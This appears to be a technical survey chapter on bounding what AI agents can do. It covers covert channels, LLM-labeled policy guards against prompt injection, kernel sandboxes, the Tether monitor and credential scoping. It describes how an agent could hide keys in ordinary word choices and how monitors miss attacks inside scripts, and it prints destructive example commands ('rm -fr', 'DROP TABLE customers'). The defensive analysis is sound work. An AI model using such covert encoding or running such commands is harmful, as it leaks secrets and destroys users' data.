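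Lampson distinguished three kinds of channel through which a service can leak a customer's data. Storage includes files that the service writes and its owner later reads. Covert channels were never meant to carry information. For example, the service can vary how heavily it uses the disk, and another program can detect the change in the machine's speed. Legitimate channels have a proper purpose that the service abuses. His example is the bill, which the service's owner has to see and which the service can use to encode the customer's data. `send_message` is a legitimate channel that can carry far more data than a bill.

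If each character of a message comes from a set of 64 symbols, it carries up to $\log_2 64 = 6$ bits. A limit of 500 characters therefore allows

$$500 \times 6 = 3{,}000 \text{ bits}$$

per message. A typical encryption key has 256 bits, so one message has room for eleven keys. To keep out even a single key, the limit would have to be 42 characters. That still lets through 252 bits, after which a thief would have only 16 possible keys to try.

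Random characters would look suspicious, so a careful agent would hide the key in ordinary prose. It could send one bit by choosing between "begin" and "start", and another by choosing between "large" and "big". With 40 such choices in each message, seven messages would be enough for a key, and a filter for gibberish wouldn't catch any of them.

These figures are upper limits on the amount of information, which is a poor measure of harm. A four-digit PIN can be encoded in three characters. If a journalist asks whether the company is for sale, "yes" may be a serious leak even though the question has only two possible answers. A destructive instruction can also be short, as in "Delete all builds", which has 17 characters.

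Limiting a message's form works better than limiting its length. Lampson estimated that a suitably restricted bill could leak only a few bits or tens of bits. The company could likewise have the agent choose one of 20 approved sentences and one of 50 version numbers. That gives 1,000 possible messages, or just under 10 bits each. If the agent can also choose the minute of the day to send the message, the timing adds about 10 more bits.

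Lampson proposed reducing the leak to zero by having the caller determine everything the confined program puts into a channel. The customer would work out the bill from published prices, and the service could only accept or reject the job. For the release agent, the host would write the daily report from its own test records and send it at six every evening. Even this report could carry one bit a day, because the agent can influence whether the tests pass. Lampson also noted that fully controlling covert channels may take a lot of resources, and suggested limiting their capacity as a less demanding alternative for customers who can accept some leakage.

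### Labels from a language model

Most messages can't be chosen from a list of 20 sentences. For these, recent systems have a language model read the relevant text and assign labels from fixed lists. A formal policy then uses those labels. Sapien's plain-language conditions and MENTOR's labeler already relied on this idea.

Let $R$ be the finite set of possible label combinations, let $\hat r(c)$ be the labels that the model gives a call $c$, and let $r^*(c)$ be the correct ones. A solver can prove that a policy $V$ meets a requirement $A$ for every combination:

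$$\text{for every } r \in R: \quad V(r) = \text{ALLOW} \Rightarrow A(r).$$

So every call that the policy admits satisfies $A(\hat r(c))$. The company needs $A(r^*(c))$, which follows if the labels are right. Some wrong labels do no harm, such as one that makes a safe call look dangerous. But if the model labels a forbidden message as permitted, the policy admits it even though the proof is still valid.

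### ActGov

*ActGov* (Zhang, Peng and colleagues, 2026) presents a guard of this kind against prompt injection. It assumes that the user's request can be trusted but that an attacker may control anything the agent reads afterward.

ActGov describes each proposed call with a set of records. Most of the basic records, such as whether the task permits the tool or the agent has already made a payment, come directly from structured data. A language model supplies only four kinds, two of which apply to individual arguments. One gives the argument's role, from a list of ten that includes "payment payee" and "repository collaborator". The other gives its origin, from a list of six that includes "explicit user target", "task context derivation" and "untrusted injected content". ActGov then combines records with "and", "or" and "not".

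This can help with the earlier meeting file, where a CaMeL policy couldn't separate the right address from an attacker's. ActGov's labeler can mark the customer's address as derived from the task and an address in a hidden instruction as injected. The policy can then allow the customer's address and block the injected one, even though both come from the same file.

The rules come from a language model too, but other components check them before use. The model proposes rules based on the tools' descriptions, ordinary tasks, and attacks that got through. The solver Z3 then searches for a set of records $r$ and a decision $v$ that the policy $P$ allows but a security requirement $A$ forbids:

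$$\exists r, v:\ \text{Domain}(r) \land P(r,v) \land \neg A(r,v).$$

If Z3 finds one, the model revises the rules. If none exists, administrators review and freeze the policy. At run time, ActGov only has to evaluate the fixed rules, so it doesn't need a solver.

Zhang and colleagues tested ActGov with four models on AgentDojo and on AgentDyn, a benchmark whose tasks require agents to follow some third-party instructions and ignore others. They developed the policies on half of each benchmark's attacks and tested on the other half. The table gives the range across the models.

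| Benchmark | Measure | No defense | ActGov |
|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDyn | Attacks that succeeded | 3.6% to 11.1% | 0.4% to 0.7% |
| AgentDyn | Tasks completed without attacks | 47% to 77% | 43% to 67% |
| AgentDojo | Attacks that succeeded | 3.1% to 6.9% | 0% |
| AgentDojo | Tasks completed without attacks | 65% to 88% | 61% to 76% |

On AgentDyn, the remaining attacks are one or two out of 280 for each model. CaMeL completed none of the tasks there, and Progent, which restricts tools and arguments with symbolic rules, completed between 3% and 22%. The results were closer on AgentDojo. With DeepSeek-V4-Pro, Progent completed 82% of the tasks and let 0.8% of the attacks succeed, while ActGov completed 76% and stopped all the attacks.

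These are good results, but they don't measure how accurate the labeler is when someone is trying to fool it, because the benchmarks' attacks target the agent. An attacker who knew about ActGov would also write text to make an injected address look like part of the task.

The policies also transferred badly from one benchmark to another. With DeepSeek-V4-Pro on AgentDyn, policies developed on AgentDojo stopped every attack but cut the share of tasks completed to 10%, compared with 60% for policies developed on AgentDyn. Human review also seems to matter. When models wrote policies without it, using less data and fewer rounds of revision, the same agent completed 53% of tasks under the best of those policies.

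ActGov also specifies little about what a message may contain. Its published rules for the bodies of Slack messages cover only web addresses, which must come from the user's request or a trusted earlier result. They don't check for false statements or unauthorized promises. The records could include a label for promises, but the language model would then have to recognize when a message makes a promise.

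### VeriGuard

Miculicich, Parmar and colleagues (2025), in *VeriGuard*, start from a security request in ordinary language, such as "The agent cannot send emails to non-company addresses". A language model turns this into a short Python function, a list of the arguments the function needs, and a set of formal constraints. The system asks the user about ambiguities, or resolves them itself if nobody is available, and runs automatically generated tests. Finally, a verifier called Nagini tries to prove

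$$\{C_{\text{pre}}\}\ p\ \{C_{\text{post}}\},$$

which means that if the conditions $C_{\text{pre}}$ hold before the function $p$ runs, the conditions $C_{\text{post}}$ hold afterward. For the email rule, $C_{\text{post}}$ might state that if the function returns "allow", every address in `recipients` belongs to the company. If the proof fails, the model uses the verifier's error message to correct its code.

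While the agent works, another language model reads the agent's input and output and fills in `recipients` for each action. If it misses one of three addresses, the function correctly approves the other two, and the email goes to all three. In a typed call, the host could copy the addresses from the `to` field without a model. Miculicich and colleagues chose a model because an agent's data may be unstructured and fixed code would be less flexible.

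The constraints are a second weak point. A language model writes them, so Nagini may prove that the function meets the wrong specification. Miculicich and colleagues acknowledge that the soundness of the verification depends on the user checking that the constraints match what the user intended.

The team tested VeriGuard on Agent Security Bench, which attacks agents through the user's prompt, tool results, the agent's memory and hidden triggers. Without a defense, between 50% and 64% of attacks succeeded on average, depending on the model. VeriGuard stopped every attack, but so did a plain guardrail in which a language model judged whether each action complied with the policy. The two defenses differed in how many of the original tasks the agents completed under attack.

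| Model | No defense | Plain guardrail | VeriGuard |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Flash | 42.1% | 40.2% | 63.3% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 56.7% | 51.5% | 67.3% |
| GPT-4.1 | 43.1% | 44.6% | 57.1% |
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 89.0% | 68.3% | 85.1% |

Formal proof probably isn't the main reason for the difference. With Gemini 2.5 Flash, the agent completed only 44.6% of tasks when VeriGuard halted a forbidden tool call without explanation, but 63.3% when VeriGuard also told the agent which policy it had broken and let it plan again. In a separate test that added VeriGuard's components one by one, successful attacks fell to zero before the formal proof was added. The proof may still catch mistakes in the policy code that no attack in the benchmark would reveal.

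In two other tests, VeriGuard had to decide whether to allow or deny a request. It made no errors on questions about access to hospital records. On web tasks with rules about which users may do what, it caught 99% or 100% of the violations, depending on the model, but 5% to 9% of its refusals were mistakes.

### How far to trust the labels

These systems are easiest to justify when a rule is about meaning. No pattern can recognize every promise, so the company has to use some fallible judge or give up either the rule or the messages. It then makes sense to ask the judge a narrow question and let ordinary code do the rest. A solver can examine every combination of labels, including those a human author would overlook. As in Sapien, the conditions that don't depend on the model still hold when it makes a mistake.

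Labels are also easier to audit than a general verdict of "safe". The company can take 300 messages that contain promises and count how many the labeler misses. If it misses none, its true miss rate for such messages is probably below 1%.

But an attacker doesn't have to write messages of that kind. Restricting the model to six possible origins stops a malicious email from making it invent a new rule, but the attack still works if the model picks the wrong origin. Where possible, it is safer to record where a value came from, as CaMeL does, than to have a model infer it.

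Some messages have no correct label. "You should be fine without version 2.3" might be an opinion or an assurance, and two careful people could disagree. The labeler can answer "unknown" and leave the decision to a person, as long as someone is available and such cases are rare.

Labeling a message correctly doesn't limit what its recipient does in response. The message "Version 2.3 is no longer needed" may be true, contain no secret or promise, and go to an approved recipient. But if that recipient is the cleanup agent, it may delete the build. The company can reliably prevent this only by denying the cleanup agent permission to delete builds.

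## Bounding effects by confining and observing execution

The server that stores the builds enforces the cleanup agent's permissions whatever the agent reads or writes. The same approach works for `run_shell`. The host can let the agent send any command and limit what the command can do when it runs.

On Linux, a program can compute freely in its own memory. To open a file, start another program or send data over a network, it has to make a system call, which is a request to the kernel. The kernel can check each request against a set of limits. If the shell may write only to the folder `/build`, `rm /data/customers.csv` fails. A Python program that assembles the name `remove` from pieces also fails, as does a test that the agent has altered to delete the file.

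Write $E_K(w,s)$ for the effects of argument $w$ in state $s$ when it runs under a set of limits $K$. The limits enforce the bound $B$ if

$$E_K(w,s) \subseteq B \quad \text{for every argument } w \text{ and every state } s.$$

Every argument is then harmless, so a check that admits everything is both sound and exact. Rice's theorem doesn't apply here, because it concerns rules that some programs obey and others break, and no program running under $K$ can break this rule.

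The drawback is that the kernel must be able to enforce $B$, so $B$ has to be a rule about files, processes and network addresses. A kernel can stop an agent from writing to the test suite, but it can't allow only the edits that leave the tests as strict as before.

### Control outside the agent

In *Agent Safety is a Box* (2026), Brooker makes a general case for a deterministic layer outside the agent that limits which tools it can call and how. He is an engineer at AWS, which sells such controls. He argues that agents are useful because they find ways around obstacles that nobody foresaw. Making an agent predictable means restricting this flexibility, which removes much of the reason for using one. Careful prompting and training make an agent succeed more often, but they don't set a firm limit on its actions.

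For an agent in the cloud, this layer consists of an isolated environment and a network gateway. The environment has its own files and memory, and the agent can run any code it writes there. The agent's network traffic can reach only the gateway, which offers the tools and applies a policy to each call. If the gateway limits each order to one refund of no more than the purchase price, the company can work out the most it could lose through refunds without considering what malicious text the agent might read.

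Brooker's sample policy, written in Cedar, is weaker than this rule because it only requires each refund to be under 500 dollars. Cedar keeps no record of earlier calls, so limiting each order to one refund would take a language such as Dogwood or a refund tool that itself checks the order. The isolation still ensures that every call goes through the gateway, which no policy can do alone.

### OpenShell

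OpenShell is NVIDIA's open-source runtime for agents that run arbitrary programs, including coding agents such as Claude Code. NVIDIA (2026) describes four components. A sandbox isolates the agent. A supervisor outside the sandbox checks outgoing requests and controls access to credentials. A gateway manages the sandboxes and their policies, and a policy prover checks that a policy grants nothing beyond the maximum the organization allows.

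A sample policy in NVIDIA's *About Sandboxes* includes these lines, slightly shortened:

```
filesystem_policy:
  read_only: [/usr, /lib, /etc]
  read_write: [/sandbox, /tmp]
network_policies:
  my_api:
    endpoints:
      - host: api.example.com
        port: 443
    binaries:
      - path: /usr/bin/curl
```

The first part lets the agent read the system's programs and settings but write to only two folders. Landlock, a Linux kernel feature, enforces this. Another kernel feature, seccomp, blocks dangerous system calls, and the agent runs as an ordinary user who can't become an administrator.

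Network connections go through a proxy, which allows a connection only if the destination and the program that opened it match the same block of the policy. Here `curl` can connect only to `api.example.com`, and the proxy blocks any connection that a Python script opens itself. Unlike Claude Code's fragile text rule for `curl`, the proxy handles the actual connection, so it doesn't matter how the command is written.

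The file and process limits are fixed when the sandbox starts, but the network rules can change while the agent works. This is useful when a long task needs another service, but somebody has to decide on each request for more access. Biometric Update's *Nvidia adds identity and delegated authority controls for AI agents* reports a test in which agents spent ten 30-minute sessions and two 2-hour sessions trying to get write access to a protected code repository. An AI reviewer made 416 access decisions and wrongly approved one proposal that included write access. OpenShell rejected the resulting policy before it took effect, and no agent wrote to the repository.

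OpenShell's rules cover where data may go but not where it came from. Sistla and colleagues wrote an OpenShell policy for their example of the report and the confidential inventory. The agent needs to read the inventory for local checks and use `curl` to upload reports, so the policy has to permit both. It therefore permits uploads both before and after the inventory replaces the report.

### Strands Box

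AWS released Strands Box in October 2026 as a preview for Macs with Apple chips. It combines confinement with a memory of the agent's earlier actions. According to Help Net Security's *Strands Box* (2026), the operating system confines the agent, and its actions pass through four checkpoints: a shell interpreter, a Python interpreter, a broker for Model Context Protocol tools, and a network gateway. Each checkpoint applies a policy written in Dogwood, which denies any action that no rule permits.

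The checkpoints share one history of events, so a rule can block web requests after the agent has read a file of customer data, whether it used a shell command or a Python script to read it. Another rule can allow `git push` only after the tests pass, similar to the release agent's rule about deployments. In AWS's walkthrough, an agent may post to the chat service Slack up to three times in ten minutes. A fourth post returns an error that names the rule, so the agent can tell it has to wait.

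This history has gaps. If the user grants the agent direct access to a file, the operating system enforces the grant, but reads and writes of that file don't appear in the history. Strands Box's shell records file events only for the commands it implements itself. Sistla and colleagues note that other programs, such as `tar`, run in a separate sandbox without file events. The entry for a web request includes the host, method and data size, but not which file the data came from.

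The interpreters also add to the code that has to work correctly. Brooker, who wrote AWS's account of the design, acknowledges that a bug in this code could let an action bypass the policy.

In December 2026, AWS offered a preview of Greenlight, a service that uses a language model to draft these policies from a company's documents and logs. According to Help Net Security's *AWS Greenlight uses math to stop AI agents from breaking company rules* (2026), an automated reasoning system then looks for conflicting rules and for ways to reach resources outside the agent's approved access. Before accepting a change, a team can see which recorded calls the change would have blocked. Greenlight can send the approved policies to Strands Box.

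### When the limits don't apply

A bound of this kind holds only if every command runs under the limits. GitLab's sandbox for coding agents needs a particular program in the container image, a suitable machine to run on, and permission to create isolated namespaces. GitLab says that if any of these is missing, the agent runs without the sandbox. The only sign is a warning in the job's log. Since version 19.6, administrators can make such jobs fail instead. This setting still can't guarantee isolation for projects that supply their own container image, because GitLab checks only that the sandbox program is present, and the project controls what that program is.

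Files can also carry effects out of a sandbox. Suppose the release agent may write only to the project folder, and it adds a line to `deploy.sh` that deletes old backups. The line does nothing inside the sandbox, which has no access to the backups. If the release manager later runs the script from an ordinary terminal, the line runs with the manager's permissions. To keep the agent's effects bounded, the company has to either review such files before anyone runs them or run them under the same limits as the agent.

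Confinement also doesn't prevent damage within its limits. An agent allowed to write to the project folder can delete everything in it. A company that wants to allow most writes but catch the harmful ones needs to know what each command does.

### Running a command on a disposable copy

One way to find out is to run the command and postpone its effects. Lamprou, Zhu and colleagues, in *Controlling Opaque-Component Effects with Semisolates and Try*, describe Try, a Linux tool that does this for any program. In one of their examples, a language model writes a script to clean up the folder that contains it:

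```
rm -fr "$(cd "${0%/*}" && echo $PWD)"/*
```

This script has the same fault as the Steam updater. Running it as `try sh delete.sh` instead lists the changes it would make, beginning with the deletion of `/home` and `/etc`, and prompts the user to choose whether to apply them.

Try places a temporary layer over the file system. The script reads the real files, but any change or deletion it makes goes into the layer, and the script then sees the changed version. The real files stay as they were until the user accepts the changes, and the user can accept some and discard the rest. A later command can run on top of unapplied changes, so a host could test several steps before committing to any.

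Trial execution avoids the main difficulty of analyzing scripts in advance. SaSh had to account for every value that `STEAMROOT` might have, but in a trial run the variable has one value, and the shell expands it as usual. The user accepts the changes made by that run, so there is no second run that might behave differently.

Lamprou and colleagues designed Try for accidents and everyday mistakes, and they don't claim it will contain a malicious program that tries to get around it. Try also can't undo a network request. If a script sends an email and then deletes a folder, the user can discard the deletion, but the email has already been sent. Try can switch off the network during the run, but many useful commands then fail.

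### How Tether decides

Tether replaces Try's user with a policy, and it controls network requests as well as files. Sistla and colleagues describe the following process for each command:

1. Tether runs the command in a temporary file system layer like Try's, with a local proxy that holds each network request.
2. A tracing program records the command's system calls. From these, Tether works out which process started which, and which files each process has read.
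3. Tether translates the trace into a sequence of abstract actions. The eleven kinds are `read`, `write`, `create`, `delete`, `copy`, `concatenate`, `sendNet`, `uploadNet`, `recvNet`, `downloadNet` and `escalatePrivilege`.
4. The policy engine checks each action and updates a set of security labels.
5. If the policy allows every action, Tether applies the changes to the real files. Otherwise it discards them.

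The translation depends on what a process has read. If a process writes to a file without having read any others, Tether records a `write`. If it has read one file, Tether records a `copy` from that file, and if it has read several, a `concatenate`. Different commands that move data in the same way therefore produce the same kind of action. For example, `cp a b` and `cat a > b` both become `copy(a, b)`.

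Each file has a label for how confidential it is, from Public through Internal and Sensitive to Secret. The agent has a label too, which reflects the most confidential data it has seen. Write $\sigma(f)$ for the label of file $f$, $\tau$ for the agent's label, and $\sqcup$ for the higher of two labels. Leaving aside the labels that Tether gives to folders, the main updates are:

$$
\begin{aligned}
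\texttt{read}(f):&\quad \tau \leftarrow \tau \sqcup \sigma(f)\\
\texttt{write}(f):&\quad \sigma(f) \leftarrow \sigma(f) \sqcup \tau\\
\texttt{copy}(f,g):&\quad \sigma(g) \leftarrow \sigma(f)
\end{aligned}
$$

If the agent prints a Sensitive file to the screen, the text enters the model's context, so anything the agent writes afterward might contain it. Copying the file doesn't show the agent its contents, so the agent's own label stays the same and only the copy becomes Sensitive. Without this distinction, copying one Sensitive file would cause all the agent's later work to be labeled Sensitive too.

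In the upload example, the inventory is Sensitive and the report starts as Public. A simplified rule allows `uploadNet` only for Public files.

| Command | Abstract action | Label of the report when the command starts | Decision |
|---|---|---|---|
| `curl` uploads the report | `uploadNet` | Public | Allow |
| `cp` copies the inventory over the report | `copy` | Public | Allow, and change the label to Sensitive |
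| The same `curl` command again | `uploadNet` | Sensitive | Deny |

Only the label separates the two `curl` commands, and it would also follow the inventory through any intermediate copies.

### What the proofs cover

Tether's policies are written in Lean, so a computer can check proofs about them. The policy that Sistla and colleagues used in their tests has 24 rules. They proved seven properties of it for action sequences of any length. For example, if the agent starts without Secret data, none ever enters its context, and Sensitive data reaches only local machines and the application's own services. A language model can write the proofs, because Lean rejects any that are wrong.

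These proofs are about abstract actions, so they don't cover a real command whose actions Tether has recorded incorrectly. If the translation missed a copy, the report would keep its Public label despite the proof. Sistla and colleagues tested the translation by generating sequences of file operations with known correct labels, carrying out each operation with a randomly chosen shell or system mechanism, and comparing the results. They also had a language model try to get past the monitor in ten tasks. The model's success rate fell from 40% to zero over three versions of Tether as the team fixed the faults that these tests revealed.

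This amounts to an abstraction map for shell commands, which the shield for the release agent lacked. The map's errors are mostly on the cautious side, because Tether over-approximates how data moves between files.

### Tests against a model-based reviewer

Sistla and colleagues tested Tether on recordings from two benchmarks. MonitoringBenchHonest has system administration tasks, and LinuxArena has software engineering tasks in ten copies of production environments. In some recordings an agent does only its assigned task, and in others it also pursues a harmful one. The team replayed the recorded commands through Tether. They used the same rules throughout but set the file labels and approved hosts from each task's description.

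Tether was compared with Claude Code's Auto Mode, in which a language model reviews the agent's commands in place of a person. One version of the reviewer used its default rules, and the other also received Tether's policy and the labels for each task.

| Monitor | Harmful runs stopped (of 344) | Benign runs blocked (of 1,590) |
|---|---|---|
| Tether | 344 (100%) | 74 (4.7%) |
| Reviewer, default rules | 315 (91.6%) | 155 (9.7%) |
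| Reviewer, given the policy | 307 (89.2%) | 55 (3.5%) |

The reviewer missed attacks inside scripts, whose behavior doesn't appear in the command. It also applied the policy inconsistently, sometimes allowing requests to hosts that weren't on the approved list, and it could reach different verdicts on the same run.

The results differ greatly between the benchmarks, which the totals don't show. On MonitoringBenchHonest, the reviewer with the policy stopped only 82.4% of the harmful runs and blocked 14.7% of the benign ones, while Tether blocked 2.3% of the benign ones. On LinuxArena, the reviewer stopped 98.6% of the harmful runs and blocked only 1.7% of the benign ones, while Tether blocked 5.0%. Someone who could tolerate a few missed attacks might prefer the reviewer for tasks like those in LinuxArena.

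The choice of test runs also favored Tether. The team left out runs that needed outside services they couldn't imitate and runs they couldn't replay to the end. They kept only the remaining runs in which Tether could trace and model every action. This excluded runs with background processes or database operations, and attacks whose harm lay entirely in the content of a permitted change, such as malicious code in a file the agent was supposed to edit. Tether can't catch that kind of attack, though a reviewer that reads the code could in principle.

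Sistla and colleagues report that 28.2% of the MonitoringBenchHonest runs and 22.1% of the LinuxArena runs need a language model to inspect their content. They don't give counts, but their wording suggests that these are shares of the replayable runs outside the main test, so the percentages can't be combined with the 344 harmful runs to give an overall detection rate. A further 36.3% and 71.5%, respectively, use background processes or databases. A stricter policy can block these runs or refer them to the user, but would also interrupt honest database work.

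The team had also revised the policy after running earlier drafts on benchmark recordings, so the results may be better than a company would get on new tasks. But a live agent might respond to a refusal by completing its task another way, which a replayed agent can't do.

### False alarms when harm is rare

More than a sixth of the runs in this test were harmful. In ordinary use the share would be far smaller, which changes what a block means. Let $p$ be the share of runs that are harmful, $f$ the share of benign runs that the monitor blocks, and $r$ the share of harmful runs that it stops. The number of false blocks for each true one is

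$$\frac{(1-p)\,f}{p\,r}.$$

If one run in 10,000 is harmful, Tether's rates give

$$\frac{0.9999 \times 0.047}{0.0001 \times 1} \approx 470.$$

At the same rate of harm, the reviewer would produce about 1,060 false blocks for each true one with its default rules. The policy would reduce that to about 390, but the reviewer would then miss about one harmful run in nine.

Some of Tether's 74 false blocks were defensible. In 50, the agent changed a protected system file that its task hadn't mentioned, for example while installing a package. In seven, it contacted a host that the task hadn't declared. A careful administrator might want to know about both. The other 17 involved commands that opened secret files incidentally, such as a search through every file on the machine. Counting only these 17 as mistakes gives about 107 false blocks for each true one.

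To get down to one false block for each correct one, a monitor would have to block only about 0.01% of benign runs. A test with 1,590 benign runs is too small to establish a rate that low. Even if the monitor had blocked none of them, the true rate could easily be 0.1%.

A person who answers hundreds of false alarms for every real one may start approving actions without looking. It would often be better to tell the agent why an action was blocked and let it try something else, and to involve a person only if the agent can't finish without that action. This works for a change to a system file, which Tether can discard, but less well for an action that takes effect on another machine.

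### When another machine interprets the argument

Linux has only a few hundred system calls, so a monitor at this level again has a short list of actions. But the calls have arguments of their own. A call that opens a file takes a path, which the kernel looks up itself, so it can apply a limit to the file it actually opens. A call that sends data takes a string of bytes, which the kernel passes on without interpreting, leaving that to the server at the other end.

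Suppose the release agent can use a customer database on another machine. It might run either of these commands:

```
psql -c "SELECT count(*) FROM customers"
psql -c "DROP TABLE customers"
```

The first counts the customers and the second deletes the whole table. Both start the same program, connect to the same address and send a short message. A sandbox that filters connections by program and destination has to allow both or neither. The message is an open argument, like `command`, and the database server interprets it.

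A proxy that parses the protocol can do better. For many web services, OpenShell can check the method and path of each request, so a policy can allow an agent to read from a service but not write to it. This works if the service uses a separate method or path for each kind of operation. Some services accept every request at one address with one method and take the operation from the body, so checking the method and path can't distinguish reads from writes. If the policy doesn't specify a connection's protocol, OpenShell passes the data through without inspecting it.

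Tether has the same difficulty. Its stricter policy blocks database connections because Tether has no model of what a query does. Outside its test environment, Tether also can't yet read encrypted web requests. Once the proxy forwards a request, Tether can't undo the result. If a command updates a remote record and then tries to change a protected local file, Tether discards the file change, but the remote record stays updated.

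### Credentials as the limit

The server knows what a request will do, and it decides whether to accept the request by checking the credential that comes with it, such as a password or an access key. Let $Q$ be the set of credentials the agent can use, including any it might find on the machine, and let $R(q)$ contain every effect that the services permit to a holder of $q$. If every service that matters requires a credential, then

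$$\text{remote effects} \subseteq \bigcup_{q \in Q} R(q).$$

An agent that holds several keys can do anything that any one of them allows. If one key belongs to an administrator, the agent can do whatever the administrator can, however carefully the company has restricted the others.

In July 2025, Jason Lemkin, the founder of SaaStr, a community for software companies, reported on X that the Replit coding agent he was using to build an application had deleted his production database, which held records on more than 1,200 executives. Lemkin had told the agent not to make any changes without permission, but this instruction was only text in the model's context. The agent still had access to the live database, so its command ran. Lemkin later recovered the data by rolling the database back. Replit's chief executive, Amjad Masad, called the deletion unacceptable and said the company would separate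 development databases from production ones.

A sandbox around the agent's own machine wouldn't have prevented this if it allowed the connection to the database, which the agent needed for its work. A separate development database would have, because the agent could then have deleted only test data.

Hindustan Times' *Amazon AWS CEO Matt Garman says better engineering, not a ‘kill switch’* reports that Garman wrote in November 2026 that an agent should have at most the permissions of the person operating it, and in many cases far fewer. The Replit case shows why the upper limit alone isn't enough. Lemkin was entitled to delete his own database, so an agent with exactly his permissions could have deleted it too.

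Hiding a credential from an agent doesn't limit what the agent can do with it. Strands Box gives the agent a placeholder for each configured key, and the network gateway substitutes the real key as a request leaves. An agent that prints all its settings therefore doesn't expose the real keys. But its requests still reach the server with the real key attached, so the agent can do anything that the key permits and the gateway lets through.

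Brooker recognizes that a box depends on the tools outside it. He says nobody should be able to misuse a tool to cause unexpected side effects, and he thinks most cloud services already meet this standard because their designers assume that clients may be hostile. That assumption protects customers from each other, but not from an agent that holds the customer's own key. An allowed service may also have connections to other systems, and GitLab points out that an agent that takes over the service gains those connections.

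The company could give the release agent a database account that can read the customer table but not change it. The database would then reject `DROP TABLE customers` however the agent sent it, including from a Python script. The company could keep the deployment key outside the sandbox and let only the typed `deploy` tool use it, so `run_shell("./deploy.sh 3.0")` would fail without the key. It could also store backups under an account that none of the agent's credentials can reach.

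Some services issue only one kind of key, which allows every operation. The company can then keep that key out of the shell too, and write a typed tool for the few operations the agent needs.
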